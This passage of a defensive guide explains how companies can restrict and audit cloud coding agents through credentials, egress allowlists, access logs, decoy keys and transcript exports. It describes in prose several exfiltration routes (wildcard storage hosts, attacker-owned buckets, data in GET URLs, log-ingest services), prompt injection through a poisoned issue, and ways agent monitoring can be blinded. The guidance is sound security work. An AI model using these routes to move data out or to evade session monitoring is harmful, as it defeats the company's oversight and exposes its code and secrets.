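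Other vendors place the identity token inside the session. Cognition's *Cloud Authentication with OIDC* explains that every session of its coding agent, Devin, receives a token that Cognition refreshes until the session ends. Warp, which makes a terminal and cloud agents, provides a command that requests a token from within a running session. Ordinary cloud tools then work without further setup, but a malicious script running in the same session could probably obtain a token in the same way.

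### Keeping the key outside the machine

With a *credential proxy*, the agent sends a request without a key, and a program outside its machine adds the key before forwarding the request. To add the key, the proxy must decrypt web traffic that would otherwise stay encrypted all the way to the service.

Anthropic's GitHub proxy swaps the session's limited git credential for the developer's real token. A thief who stole the limited credential could not use it directly with GitHub. The proxy also refuses API requests for repositories that aren't attached to the session, and it blocks GitHub's GraphQL interface entirely, even if the session supplies its own token.

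For other services, Anthropic's customers can store a *network secret*, which is a key together with the hosts that should receive it. Anthropic adds the key to matching requests after they leave the machine, so the key isn't in any file or variable on the machine. The billing company could store its payments test key for one host, and the agent could call the payments API without having the key. Nobody can view the key after it is saved.

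A network secret's main weakness is that it applies to every session in the environment, whoever started it, until someone deletes it. If the whole engineering team shares an environment, a session that fixes a typo in the documentation can also call the payments API. Using separate environments for different kinds of work would limit this. Secrets also have to be deleted explicitly, because archiving an environment leaves them attached to sessions that are still running.

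Network secrets don't work for every key. The proxy doesn't add them to requests from setup scripts or to requests for the main public package registries. The service that the key is for must also accept connections from the internet, which rules out many internal systems. Claude Tag's proxy carries only web traffic, according to Anthropic's *How agent identity works*, so an agent there can't connect to a database using the database's own protocol. The company would have to put a web service or remote MCP server in front of the database.

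| Method | Who holds the long-lived secret | What a malicious script in the session could obtain |
|---|---|---|
| Environment variable | The agent's machine | The key itself, usable until someone replaces it |
| Installation token | The company's token service | A token for the listed repositories, usable for up to an hour |
| Federation from inside the session | Nobody | Temporary credentials, and probably new ones while the session lasts |
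| Credential proxy | The proxy's operator | No key, but the ability to send requests that the proxy will authenticate |

As the last row shows, a proxy prevents the theft of a key but not its misuse. If the payments key can issue refunds, a session can issue them through the proxy without ever seeing the key. The company still has to limit the key's permissions at the payments service.

A service can also return a new credential in its reply. To test an AWS connection, Anthropic has customers temporarily allow requests to AWS's Security Token Service, which issues credentials. Anthropic advises customers to stop allowing those requests after the test, because if the connection's AWS role is allowed to take on another role, Claude's sandbox can read the credentials AWS returns. For Google Cloud, Anthropic offers a setting that makes the proxy refuse requests for new credentials.

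### Turning a credential into a record

Services usually log which credential was used for each request. If each session has its own credential, labeled with the session's ID, the service's access log becomes a partial record of what each session did. When all sessions share one key, the log doesn't show which session made a request.

On AWS, the simplest label is the *role session name*, which appears in the log entry for each request made with the temporary credentials. A company can also attach up to 50 *session tags*, such as the repository or the developer's name, but AWS doesn't pass these on by default when a program uses one role to take on another. The best label for sessions that move between roles is the *source identity* because, according to AWS's *Monitor and control actions taken with assumed roles*, nobody can change it once it is set.

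Whoever requests the credentials normally chooses the role session name. If the request comes from the agent's machine, a malicious script could use another session's ID as the name. A token service outside the machine should set the name, or the trust policy should require a specific name.

Suppose the billing company's token service has issued credentials to a session with the ID `sess-7f3a91`. When the agent downloads a sample invoice, CloudTrail, AWS's log of activity in an account, might contain this entry, shortened and with invented values:

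```json
{
  "eventTime": "2026-10-06T14:21:37Z",
  "eventSource": "s3.amazonaws.com",
  "eventName": "GetObject",
  "userIdentity": {
    "type": "AssumedRole",
    "arn": "arn:aws:sts::123456789012:assumed-role/agent-tests/sess-7f3a91",
    "accessKeyId": "ASIAEXAMPLE"
  },
  "requestParameters": {
    "bucketName": "billing-test-data",
    "key": "invoices/leap-day.json"
  }
}
```

The `arn` line ends with the role and the session ID. The access key ID also appears in the entry that CloudTrail wrote when AWS issued the credentials, so an investigator can match the download to that entry. The token service's log then shows which developer's task the credentials were for. CloudTrail doesn't record downloads of individual files unless the company turns on data events for the storage bucket. Without data events, the company would see that the session had obtained credentials but not which invoices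 it downloaded.

With Claude Tag, Anthropic logs a `ccr_agent_proxy_anthropic_oidc_token_exchanged` event each time the proxy exchanges an identity token for cloud credentials. Administrators can retrieve the event, which includes the agent's ID, through Anthropic's Compliance API. AWS CloudTrail records the same exchange as `AssumeRoleWithWebIdentity`. The two logs should match, allowing for short delays in each. A sign-in that appears only in CloudTrail would be a reason to check the trust policy, because AWS may have accepted a token from another organization.

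These records don't always identify a single session. Claude can reuse one sign-in for most of an hour across threads in the same channel, and neither log records a new sign-in when it does. CloudTrail labels the requests with the ID of the session that first signed in, so a download that one thread requested may appear under another thread's ID. The identity token also contains no information about the person who made the request, according to Anthropic's *Identity token reference*. An investigator might be able to trace a download only to a Slack channel and an hour, and would need the session transcripts to narrow it down further.

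Devin's tokens contain more detail, including the session ID and the email address of the person who started the session. Cognition claims that cloud logs therefore attribute every action to a specific session, but this depends on which details the cloud service logs. By default, the token's subject contains only the organization's ID, so a log that recorded only the subject would not identify the session or the person. Customers can add both to the subject, and they should run a test session to see what their cloud provider records.

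GitHub Actions had a similar gap. A company could trace a token to a workflow run but not to the job within it until GitHub (2025) added the job's ID, `check_run_id`, to the token.

Installation tokens have no field for a session name, so the company's token service should log the session ID, the repositories and a hash of each token, a fingerprint that identifies the token without revealing it. If a token leaks, the company can then trace it to its session.

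A credential proxy can also log each request it handles. In a sample log from Infisical, which sells software for managing secrets, one entry lists the agent's name, the host and path, the response status and the key the proxy added. Another shows a request the proxy blocked, which the target service could not have logged because the request never reached it.

### How access logs score on the five tests

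The main weakness of these records is that they show only work that requires a credential, and only in services that keep detailed logs. An agent may need no credential to read the whole codebase, run a malicious script and post the results to a public website.

Attribution is strong when each session has its own credential and something outside the machine sets the label. It is weaker when sessions share a sign-in, as in Claude Tag's channels. It is weaker still with network secrets, because the payments service would receive the same key from every session in the environment.

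The best reason to use these logs is that they are independent of the agent's vendor. Amazon writes CloudTrail, so a fault in Anthropic's harness can't alter it. Anthropic describes its export of network events as best effort and advises customers to check the connected service's own log to confirm whether Claude made a request. For Copilot customers, an Azure log is less independent than another cloud provider's, because Microsoft owns GitHub.

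How quickly log entries appear varies by service. Anthropic tells customers to allow a few minutes for a sign-in to appear in CloudTrail, which is soon enough to interrupt a long session but perhaps not a short one. Customers largely decide how long to keep the log, since they can copy it to separate storage. The agent's role should have no permission to delete that copy.

### Shared, broad and borrowed credentials

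A separate service account for the agent takes little effort to set up. It lets a company identify the agent's actions in logs and cancel the agent's access without affecting other systems. Many companies will be tempted to reuse a key they already have, such as the one their CI system uses for the test database. The database's log would then show the same user for the agent and for CI, and if the company suspected the agent and canceled the key, it would also stop its own tests.

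A credential issued for a narrow purpose can still grant broad permissions. An engineer who wants the agent to save test results might give its role permission to write to any storage bucket. AWS uses the same addresses for all its customers, so the agent could upload invoices to a bucket in an attacker's account if the attacker had configured the bucket to accept them. Limiting the role to the `billing-test-data` bucket would prevent this. Developers can choose the GitHub token's permissions in Copilot's setup steps, so GitHub suggests that enterprises encourage them to grant only the minimum.

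Developers also let agents use their access. When someone sends Claude Tag a direct message, the session runs under that person's account and connectors, and other services record its actions under that person's name. Even in channels, a task can use a member's personal connectors. A developer who asks the agent to summarize a bug report may give it access to every document she can open, even those unrelated to the bug.

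A credential issued for each session can name both the agent and the employee who asked for the work. If the agent uses a service account instead, its actions are logged separately from those of employees, but the log doesn't identify who asked for them. A personal account identifies the employee, but an investigator can't easily tell whether she or the agent acted. Where a service accepts only personal tokens, the developer can at least create a separate one for the agent, with its own name, an early expiry date and access only to what the task requires.

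## Restricting and recording network traffic

A malicious script that posts the company's code to a public website has to send it through the vendor's network, where the customer can usually restrict which hosts the agent may contact. Branch rules and logs of credential use would not catch such a script.

Vendors commonly restrict network traffic from an agent's environment with an *egress proxy*, a server that outbound traffic must pass through. The proxy checks each request against an *egress allowlist*, the list of outside hosts that the environment may contact.

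### How an egress proxy filters a request

Suppose the agent runs `npm install` to download a package from the public registry at `registry.npmjs.org`. A typical proxy handles the request in these steps:

1. The npm program sends its request to the proxy, either because an environment variable such as `HTTPS_PROXY` gives the proxy's address or because the network redirects all web traffic there.
2. The connection to the registry will be encrypted, so npm first asks the proxy to open a tunnel to `registry.npmjs.org`. If the network redirected the traffic instead, the proxy reads the host name from the opening message of the encrypted connection, where it normally appears as plain text.
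3. The proxy looks for the name on the allowlist.
4. If the name is there, the proxy connects to the registry and passes encrypted data in both directions. If not, it refuses, and npm reports an error.

A proxy works as a barrier only if programs have no other way out. GitHub's *Agentic Workflow Firewall* describes a tool that customers run themselves. It uses Linux's packet-filtering rules to redirect web traffic to the proxy program Squid, so programs don't need to be configured to use the proxy. Codex cloud seems to rely on programs reading the proxy's address from an environment variable, `HTTP_PROXY`. In *Codex internet access not working*, a thread on OpenAI's user forum, developers who had switched on internet access still got "network unreachable" errors, and one reply advised sending requests from Node, which runs JavaScript, through `HTTP_PROXY`. Blocking the connection is the safe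 result, but a frustrated developer might respond by allowing every host, even though the allowlist didn't cause the error.

A proxy has to decrypt traffic to read more than the host name. It presents its own certificate in place of the website's, which works only if the agent's machine trusts that certificate. Some programs still reject it. Once the traffic is decrypted, the proxy can read the request, encrypt it again and send it on. Squid's name for this is SSL Bump. Decryption gives whoever runs the proxy access to any passwords and code in the traffic.

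| Information | Available without decryption | Available with decryption |
|---|---|---|
| Host name and port | Yes | Yes |
| Time, and volume of data in each direction | Yes | Yes |
| Full address, including the path | No | Yes |
| Method, such as GET (fetch) or POST (send) | No | Yes |
| Content | No | Yes |
| Program that made the request | Only with help from software on the machine | Only with help from software on the machine |

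Traffic volume can be revealing even when nobody can read the contents. A session that installs packages receives far more data than it sends, so a 40 MB upload to a package registry would be suspicious.

Enforcing rules about methods or paths on an encrypted site requires decrypting the traffic. *Codex CLI Network Proxy* (Vaughan, 2026) explains that the version of Codex that runs on a developer's computer turns off SOCKS5, a general-purpose proxy protocol, in read-only mode because the proxy can't tell whether a request inside an encrypted tunnel only reads. Codex cloud offers a similar limit on methods, and Copilot's firewall accepts rules for individual paths, so both vendors probably have access to full addresses for at least some traffic, whether or not they keep them.

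### How the vendors' controls compare

The table below follows the documentation of GitHub, Anthropic and OpenAI, together with Cursor's *Secrets & Network*.

| | Copilot | Claude | Cursor | Codex cloud |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Who sets the list | Repository administrators and organization owners | The user, or an organization Owner for a shared environment | Users and team admins; saved environments can have their own list | Users, for each environment |
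| Whether users can override it | Repository administrators can, unless the organization prevents it | Yes, by using a different environment | Yes, unless an Enterprise admin locks the policy | Yes, if an admin permits internet access |
| What the agent can reach by default | GitHub, package and container registries, and a few related hosts | A long list that includes package registries and cloud services | Any host | No hosts |
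| What escapes the list | MCP servers and setup steps | GitHub operations, MCP connectors, hosts with a network secret, and Anthropic's API | Cursor's own services and source control providers | Setup scripts |
| What the vendor reports | Each blocked address and the command that tried it | No connection log in its network documentation | No connection log in its network documentation | No connection log in its network documentation |

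Copilot's firewall covers only processes that the agent starts through its Bash tool, which it uses to run commands. The firewall therefore applies to a malicious dependency that runs when the agent starts `npm test`, but not to one that runs code while a setup step installs it. It also doesn't cover an MCP server on the machine that fetches web pages for the agent. npm's `--ignore-scripts` option reduces the setup risk by preventing packages from running code as they install, although some packages need that code to work. GitHub warns that sophisticated attacks may bypass the firewall.

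Organization owners gained control of this firewall in April 2026, through the settings announced in GitHub's *Organization firewall settings for Copilot cloud agent*. By default, repository administrators still decide for their own repositories, so an owner who wants a single policy has to set one. At the billing company, the owner could force the firewall on and stop repository administrators from adding their own rules. Repository administrators can't delete entries from the organization's list.

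Anthropic doesn't let an administrator impose one allowlist on every environment. An Owner can create a shared environment with a strict allowlist and make it the default, but a developer can still create a personal environment with full internet access. Claude Tag channels are easier to control because they can't use personal environments. Unlike Copilot's setup steps, Claude's setup scripts are subject to the environment's network setting, and Anthropic notes that package installs fail when access is set to "None".

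Cursor has three network modes, which let agents reach any host, the default domains plus the customer's list, or the customer's list alone. An environment's own mode overrides the user's, which overrides the team's, so a team admin who selects the strictest mode may not have restricted anyone. The Enterprise lock prevents users from overriding the team's setting. Cursor says the lock gives admins full control but explains its effect only on users' settings, so an admin would need to test whether it also overrides environments that have their own mode.

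With Codex cloud, a workspace admin decides whether users may turn on internet access. Once the admin allows it, users choose the domains and methods themselves, according to OpenAI's *Admin Setup*. They can start with an empty list, a preset of 71 domains called "Common dependencies", or unrestricted access. They can also limit requests to GET, HEAD and OPTIONS, which normally retrieve information without changing anything. A later Chinese edition of the guide, OpenAI's *智能体互联网访问*, has the same defaults, presets and method limit. Setup scripts can reach the internet even when this access is off, so a company that leaves it off still has to trust the packages its setup script installs.

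### Allowing one host or a wildcard

Cursor's agents upload screenshots, videos and references to logs to a storage bucket on AWS. A team that restricts network access has to allow the bucket's host or do without those uploads. Either of these allowlist entries would work:

```
cloud-agent-artifacts.s3.us-east-1.amazonaws.com
*.s3.us-east-1.amazonaws.com
```

The second entry begins with a wildcard, so it matches every bucket in the same AWS region. The other bucket names in this comparison are invented:

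| Destination | With the exact host | With the wildcard |
|---|---|---|
| `cloud-agent-artifacts.s3.us-east-1.amazonaws.com` | Allowed | Allowed |
| `billing-test-data.s3.us-east-1.amazonaws.com` | Blocked | Allowed |
| `attackers-bucket.s3.us-east-1.amazonaws.com` | Blocked | Allowed |
| `attackers-bucket.s3.eu-west-1.amazonaws.com` | Blocked | Blocked |

Cursor warns against the wildcard because anyone with an AWS account can create a bucket in that region, and an agent under an attacker's influence could send stolen data to the attacker's bucket. Restricting the agent's AWS role wouldn't prevent this, because the attacker could supply a separate key or configure the bucket to accept uploads from anyone.

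Claude's default list has an even broader entry, `*.amazonaws.com`, which also matches buckets in other regions. It also includes `*.googleapis.com` and `*.r2.cloudflarestorage.com`, which cover Google and Cloudflare storage. A new Claude environment therefore allows the kind of upload that Cursor warns about. The company can prevent this by clearing the "Allow package managers" checkbox, which removes the default list, and entering only the hosts its project needs.

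The meaning of an entry can also differ between vendors. In Copilot's firewall, `example.com` covers all its subdomains, while in a Claude environment an administrator adds `*.example.com` to cover them. A team that copies its list from Claude to Copilot could therefore allow many more hosts than it intended. Copilot also accepts a full web address, such as `https://packages.example.com/billing/`, which restricts the agent to that path and anything below it.

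### How an allowed host can still receive stolen data

A proxy can allow a single storage bucket by its exact host name because the bucket's name is part of the host name. Many other services put all their customers on one host and distinguish them by path or account. On a code-hosting site, for example, the company's repositories and an attacker's have the same host name, so a proxy that filters only by host has to allow both or neither.

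Claude's default list includes some hosts that exist to receive data, such as those of Datadog and Honeycomb, whose customers send them logs and measurements from running software. An attacker could open an account with such a service and have a script send stolen data to it. The proxy would treat this traffic the same as the company's own.

Limiting the HTTP methods an agent can use prevents some data leaks, but not all. It would block the upload in OpenAI's example of a poisoned GitHub issue, because that command uses POST. However, a GET request, which is meant for retrieving data, can also send data in its URL. An attacker can collect that data if they can read the host's access logs or any page that displays what visitors requested.

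PromptArmor's *Configuring Codex securely across every platform and use case* claims that the "Common dependencies" preset leaves several such routes open and that attacks demonstrated by researchers still work. PromptArmor is a security company with an interest in finding problems, but the claim is plausible because the preset includes `github.com`, `gitlab.com` and `sourceforge.net`, where anyone can open an account.

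Blocking known risky sites is weaker protection than a short allowlist. OpenAI's *Running Codex safely*, which covers how OpenAI manages Codex internally, includes a configuration that blocks `pastebin.com`, a site for sharing text. Such a blocklist can stop a careless upload, but an attacker could use any site that isn't on it. An allowlist is safest when every host on it belongs either to the company using the agent or to a service that gives each customer a separate host name.

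### Whether customers can get a log of allowed connections

For ordinary cloud sessions, none of the four vendors' network documentation describes a log where customers can see allowed connections. If a script sends data to an allowed host, the customer can't expect to get a record of it from the vendor's proxy.

Copilot comes closest, but it reports only blocked requests. When the firewall blocks a request, GitHub adds a warning to the description of a new pull request or in a comment on an existing one. The warning includes the address and the command that tried to reach it, which is often enough to distinguish a missing dependency from a more serious problem. If a session never produces a pull request, GitHub would have nowhere to show the warning.

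Cursor's *Security overview* lists records that Cursor keeps, including session activity, commits, sign-ins, administrative changes and diagnostics for each run, but it doesn't list network connections. OpenAI tells users to review the agent's work log, but this log, like other session logs, can miss connections that a program makes without printing anything.

Anthropic may keep a network record that customers can't see. An older version of Anthropic's *Configure cloud environments* stated that the security proxy provided "a DNS-level audit trail of requested hostnames". The current version omits that line, and neither version explains how customers can obtain the trail. Claude Tag is a partial exception because it exports network events on a best-effort basis. A company choosing a vendor should ask, preferably before signing the contract, what connection records exist and whether it could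 get them after an incident.

Some tools that customers run themselves keep much better records. GitHub's Agentic Workflow Firewall logs all web traffic, whether allowed or blocked. The company's Agentic Workflows product uses this firewall for agents built on Copilot, Claude, Codex and Gemini, according to GitHub's *Network Permissions*. NemoClaw, NVIDIA's software for running agents in a sandbox, logs a request's host and port, the program that made it and whether the sandbox allowed it, according to NVIDIA's *How do I get a real-time audit log of every network request* (2026).

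### A private package registry

A company that can't get the vendor's log can still record the traffic that reaches its own services. Package downloads are a good place to start because they account for much of a coding agent's ordinary network use. A private registry, such as Artifactory or Nexus, stores the company's own packages and can fetch public ones on request. If the agent has to use the registry, its log records which packages and versions each credential downloaded, along with any requests for misspelled or unknown packages.

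To enforce this, the company has to remove the public registries from the allowlist and add its own:

- For Copilot, turn off the recommended allowlist and add the registry's address.
- For Claude, choose "Limited" access, clear "Allow package managers" and add the registry's host.
- For Cursor, choose "Allowlist only" and add the host.
- For Codex, start from an empty list and add the host.

These settings don't cover Copilot's setup steps or Codex's setup scripts. A package manager configuration file in the repository can direct ordinary installs to the private registry during setup, but it can't stop a malicious package from contacting another host.

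Claude's setup script can't use the environment's variables or network secrets, so a registry token would have to be in the script, where anyone who uses the environment can read it. Installing packages after Claude starts would probably avoid this problem. Cursor has separate build secrets, which it provides while building the environment but not to the running agent. Cursor's *Private Connectivity* offers Enterprise customers a private connection to registries that aren't on the public internet.

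The registry's log can also undercount the sessions that used a package. Anthropic reuses the disk snapshot from setup for about a week, so a single download may supply dozens of sessions. If a package turns out to be malicious, the company should check every session that started from the snapshot, including those with no download in the log.

### A gateway in front of internal services

A *gateway* is a server that receives requests for internal services, checks who is making them and passes them on. The company can give the agent access to the gateway alone instead of opening each service to the internet. The encrypted connection ends at the gateway, so the company can log each request's method, path and content without the certificate substitution that a proxy needs.

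Cursor describes one way to set this up with Cloudflare Tunnel, a service that connects a private network to the internet without accepting incoming connections:

1. The company runs a connector inside its network, which opens an outbound connection to Cloudflare.
2. The company assigns a public host name to the internal service and requires a token for access.
3. It stores the token as a Cursor secret and adds the host name to the agent's allowlist.
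4. The agent calls the host name like any other website, and Cloudflare passes the request through the connector.

The company would put its gateway between the connector and the service. If the agent then sent a test invoice to the payments service during the leap-day session, the gateway might log the following, with invented values:

```json
{
  "time": "2026-10-06T14:23:09Z",
  "session": "sess-7f3a91",
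  "source_ip": "203.0.113.7",
  "method": "POST",
  "path": "/test-invoices",
  "status": 201,
  "bytes_received": 1842
}
```

The gateway can fill in the `session` field only if each session has its own credential. Request content may include customer data, so many companies will prefer to log only its size, as in this example.

Databases usually need a different kind of tunnel because they don't use web requests. Cursor suggests a program that accepts connections on the agent's machine and forwards them to the database. The gateway or the database can log these connections, but a vendor's proxy might record only the encrypted tunnel. The company should limit the tunnel to the services the agent needs, since a tunnel to the whole internal network would undo much of the benefit of an allowlist.

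### Using the vendor's published IP ranges

Some vendors publish the IP addresses their agents' requests come from. Cursor provides its list as a file that a program can download, so a company could search its web server and database logs for those addresses to find requests that may have come from Cursor's agents. A match on a service that no agent should use would be worth investigating.

The file groups addresses by cluster, not by customer, so a match shows at most that a request came from Cursor's cloud, not that the company's own agent sent it. An attacker with a Cursor account might have an address in the same range. Cursor also changes its addresses from time to time and advises against relying on them as the main security mechanism. An investigator needs the ranges that applied on the day of the request, so the company should save a dated copy of the file whenever it changes.

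Cursor offers a separate proxy with a shorter list of addresses for traffic to repository hosts. OpenAI publishes IP address ranges for its GitHub connector, which companies can use to restrict where connections to their repositories come from. This makes a stolen repository token harder to use from elsewhere, but it doesn't limit what the agent sends to other hosts.

### How proxies and gateways score on the five tests

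| Test | Vendor's proxy | Customer's gateway |
|---|---|---|
| Coverage | Filters most web traffic, but Copilot reports only blocked requests and the others document no connection log | Records every request that reaches it and nothing else |
| Attribution | Good for Copilot's warnings, which appear in the session's pull request with the command | Good if each session has its own credential |
| Delay | Copilot's warning needs a pull request to appear in | Usually seconds |
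| Independence | None, because the agent's provider runs the proxy | High, because the company writes the log |
| Retention | Copilot's warnings stay with the pull request, but people with write access can edit its description | The company decides |

The two controls work best together. An agent that can reach the public npm registry can install packages without leaving a record in the company's private registry. If the allowlist contains only the company's registry and gateway, their logs cover most of the agent's ordinary web traffic, except for traffic that bypasses the allowlist, such as that from Claude's MCP connectors and Copilot's setup steps.

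The company relies on the vendor to enforce the allowlist, but it can test whether the vendor does. An engineer sets up a web server that isn't on the allowlist, then tries to contact it through the agent's command tool, a setup script and an MCP server. The web server's log shows which attempts arrived, so the test doesn't rely on the vendor's report. Repeating the test from a developer's account would show whether the developer can override the company's list.

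### Decoy credentials

An allowlist and a gateway can both miss a theft that goes through an allowed host the company doesn't run. A *decoy credential* may reveal the theft later. It is a working key with no legitimate use, which the company leaves where a thief is likely to find it. Any attempt to use the key raises an alert.

On AWS, the company could create a user with no permissions, generate an access key for it and set an alert for any CloudTrail entry that contains the key's ID. A setup script would then write the key to a file on the agent's machine. The file should have a tempting name, but it shouldn't be in the standard location for AWS credentials, because ordinary AWS tools would load the key automatically and set off false alarms. The key also shouldn't be stored as a Codex secret, because Codex removes secrets before the agent starts.

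Each environment should have its own decoy, so that the alert shows which environment the key came from. The alert may not identify the session, because every session that starts from the same saved disk has the same file. In Cursor's environments, an IP address in the CloudTrail entry that falls within Cursor's published ranges suggests that somebody used the key from inside a session, while any other address suggests that the key has left the machine.

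An alert doesn't always mean an attack, because an agent that gets an access error might search the machine for another key and try the decoy without any outside influence. The company would still want to know, because the agent might do the same with a real key. A decoy also can't detect theft that doesn't involve using it, such as when a script uploads the source code and ignores any keys.

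## Collecting the provider's session logs

A registry log, a gateway or a decoy key can record only what passes in or out of the agent's machine. A customer needs the provider's session log to find out which files the agent read and edited on the machine and which commands it ran.

### What a session log contains

In the leap-day session, the log would have four kinds of entry:

| Entry | Example | Who produces it |
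|---|---|---|
| Request | "The date parser rejects 29 February" | The developer, or whoever wrote the issue or review comment |
| Model's text | "I'll run the date tests first" | The model |
| Tool call | Run `npm test` | The model writes it, and the harness executes and records it |
| Tool result | "1 failing: 2028-02-29" | The program that ran, whose output the harness copies |

The tool call is the strongest evidence of the four. The harness runs the call it has recorded, so an entry for `npm test` means the command started, unless the harness was faulty. The result is weaker evidence because it contains whatever the program printed, and a malicious program can print a list of passing tests without running any.

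Even when the log records a command, it may show little of what happened. As in the earlier `npm test` example, the harness logs the command but not the programs it starts. When the agent runs `sh fix.sh`, the log will include the script's contents if the agent wrote or opened the file with its own tools, but may not if it downloaded the file. A command can also start a program that keeps running after the call returns, and the log doesn't record what that program does later.

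The model's text is the weakest evidence of what the agent did. A model generates an explanation the same way as any other text, and the harness doesn't check it against the tool calls. In a sample transcript in Anthropic's *Retrieve session transcripts*, the model reads a test file and then writes that it has updated the test, but the sample contains no call that edits anything. Anthropic probably shortened the example, but if a real log had this mismatch, an investigator should rely on the tool calls rather than the model's text and check the commit.

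Prompt injection makes the model's explanations even less reliable, because hidden instructions can also control what the model writes in them. An explanation can still provide a lead. If the model mentions a web page just before an odd command, investigators can check that page for hidden instructions. They can't compare the explanation with the model's *thinking blocks*, the reasoning that some models write before they answer, because Anthropic's exports leave these out.

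### What customers can export

A developer can usually read her own session on the vendor's website, but a security team needs every developer's sessions in its own log system. The table below is based on GitHub's *Audit log events for agents*, OpenAI's *Compliance API documentation* and *Governance*, and Anthropic's *Compliance API FAQ* and page on transcripts.

| | Copilot | Codex | Claude Code cloud sessions | Claude Tag |
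|---|---|---|---|---|
| Content | Prompts, responses and tool calls | Prompts, responses, user, time, model and token use | No transcript, only events such as the creation of a session | Prompts, responses, tool calls and results |
| Delay | Continuous stream, with no stated delay | Minutes | Events within a minute | No stated delay |
| How long the customer can fetch it | 48 hours | 30 days | Events for 6 years | No fixed period |
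| Plan | GitHub Enterprise Cloud, with managed users or data residency | ChatGPT Enterprise or Edu | Claude Enterprise | Claude Enterprise |
| Size limit | 1 MB per record | None documented | Not applicable | 10,000 bytes per tool input or result, or about 1 MiB on request |

All three companies reserve these exports for their largest customers. For example, a small company on Anthropic's Team plan can run cloud sessions but can't retrieve transcripts through the Compliance API, Anthropic's auditing interface.

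GitHub has the fullest export for a vendor-run coding agent. It can stream session data to the customer's log system, and an enterprise owner can request the last 48 hours through an API. Both cover the cloud agent as well as Copilot in code editors and on the command line. An administrator turns on "Copilot Usage Records Streaming" and "Copilot Usage Records API" in GitHub's AI Controls, then sets the stream's destination in the audit log settings. The stream is in public preview and requires either accounts that the company creates and manages or GitHub's data residency service, so a company whose developers use their personal GitHub accounts would not qualify.

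Each streamed record is one request or response, with the user's ID, the time and the message body. GitHub lists no field for a session ID, so the company has to find an identifier inside the body or group records by user and time. Grouping them this way becomes unreliable when one developer runs several sessions at once.

GitHub trims the body of any record that would exceed 1 MB and sets a `truncated` field to true. The harness normally sends the whole conversation to the model at every step, so records from late in a long session are probably the most likely to reach the limit. Earlier records may contain the missing text, which is a reason to keep every record instead of only the last.

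OpenAI's compliance export seems to have less detail. For Codex, OpenAI lists prompts, responses, identifiers and token use, but not commands, their output or changed files. Its usage dashboards count cloud tasks, but OpenAI doesn't say whether the export includes what happened in them. The export probably excludes Codex runs that use an API key, because it covers a company's ChatGPT workspace, but OpenAI doesn't specify this either.

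OpenAI provides the Codex logs as files that each cover a period of time, and describes them as immutable. It added the logs in December 2025, according to an update to *New compliance and administrative tools for ChatGPT Enterprise* (2024). OpenAI keeps the files for 30 days, so a company that wants a longer history has to download them continuously.

### Anthropic's gap

Anthropic's Compliance API returns full transcripts of Claude Code sessions that run on developers' own computers, which companies could monitor themselves, but no transcripts of Claude Code's cloud sessions. Anthropic keeps the transcripts for six years by default. Anthropic's *Compliance API coverage extends to Claude Cowork and Claude Code* listed Claude Code on the web as an exclusion when the coverage began, and the current documentation still lists it as one.

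The API's "remote sessions" category covers Claude Tag and the cloud version of Cowork, Anthropic's agent for general office work, but not Claude Code's cloud sessions. An administrator who queries this category and gets results might wrongly conclude that coding sessions are included.

Claude Tag sessions have transcripts, but a company's export script can miss some of them. If the script requests sessions by user ID, Anthropic leaves out every session that belongs to an agent, including those that start when someone mentions Claude in a Slack channel. The list also has no filter for recent activity. A script that fetches each transcript only once, when the session first appears, would miss anything that happens later.

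For Claude Code's cloud sessions, the company can still use the Activity Feed, a list of events in the same API. Anthropic's *Query compliance activities* includes events for when someone creates or deletes a Claude Code session or changes its settings. The feed contains no prompts or responses, and it starts recording only when the company enables the API. Even after a session's transcript is gone, the feed can show that the session existed.

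A developer can also pull a cloud session into her own terminal, but this is a poor way to preserve evidence. In a long session, the harness replaces older messages with a summary so that the conversation still fits in the model's input. According to Anthropic's documentation, the terminal receives only the summary of those messages, while the originals stay on Anthropic's website.

Anthropic doesn't offer cloud sessions to organizations that have zero data retention, manage their own encryption keys, or use its configuration for HIPAA, the American health privacy law.

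A company that uses Cursor, Devin or Jules, Google's cloud coding agent, should ask the vendor about each row of the table above. It should also expect to convert between formats, since even one vendor may use several. Anthropic's transcripts store a tool's name in the `name` field and its input as a string. The data that Anthropic sends for live checking stores the name in `tool_name` and the input as an object, so a search that works on one format would find nothing in the other.

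### Linking a commit to its session

A reviewer who finds a suspicious line of code needs to get from the commit to the session that produced it. In Copilot's commits, the session link is on a line that begins with `Agent-Logs-Url`, according to GitHub's *Trace any Copilot coding agent commit to its session logs*. This is a *trailer*, a labeled line at the end of a commit message that programs can read. For the leap-day fix, the message might look like this, with an invented name:

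```
Accept 29 February in invoice dates

Co-authored-by: Dana Reyes <dana@billing-co.example>
Agent-Logs-Url: <address of the session log>
```

The following command lists each commit with its link, if it has one:

```bash
git log --format='%h %(trailers:key=Agent-Logs-Url,valueonly)'
```

The link, which GitHub calls permanent, is useful only while the log behind it exists. A company that depends on these links should save the log when it merges the code. It should also check how its merge settings affect commit messages, because squashing a pull request into one commit can lose the trailers from the main branch. The original commits normally remain visible in the pull request.

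Anyone who can write a commit can type a trailer, so the link is reliable only if the commit has Copilot's valid signature.

### Telemetry from inside the session

Some harnesses can send event records to the customer while a session runs. They usually use *OpenTelemetry*, an open standard for sending measurements and events from a program to a server called a collector. Anthropic's *Monitoring* explains how Claude Code exports metrics, events and, optionally, traces, which connect the steps of a single operation.

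Environment variables control the export, and customers can set environment variables for Claude's cloud environments. The billing company could try these:

```
CLAUDE_CODE_ENABLE_TELEMETRY=1
OTEL_LOGS_EXPORTER=otlp
OTEL_EXPORTER_OTLP_ENDPOINT=https://telemetry.billing-co.example
```

The company would also have to add the collector's host to the environment's allowlist. Anthropic has a telemetry setting for Cowork in the cloud, but a company should run a test session to check whether Claude Code's cloud sessions send any telemetry.

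Telemetry usually contains less than a transcript. Anthropic says its telemetry includes truncated summaries of tool inputs and details about results, such as size and success. Optional settings can add prompts, responses and, up to a size limit, the content of results. But telemetry includes some details that transcripts lack, such as token costs and workspace paths.

The main advantage is that the company receives a copy immediately, so deleting the session later doesn't remove it. The main weakness is that a malicious program on the agent's machine might stop the export or send false events to the collector, as it might with a monitor installed there. Anthropic reduces this risk a little by withholding the telemetry variables from the commands that Claude Code runs, although a program with full control of the machine could probably still find them. If an organization sets the collector's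 address in its central settings, Claude Code ignores any conflicting address from a developer.

### Checking a conversation before the model receives it

Claude Enterprise customers can have Anthropic send each conversation to a server of their own for approval. Anthropic calls this feature *inference hooks*, because the check comes before inference, the step in which the model produces a reply. According to Anthropic's *Inference hooks* and Anthropic's *Develop an Inference hooks integration*, it fits into the agent loop as follows:

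1. The harness sends the conversation to Anthropic.
2. Anthropic sends a copy to the customer's server and waits.
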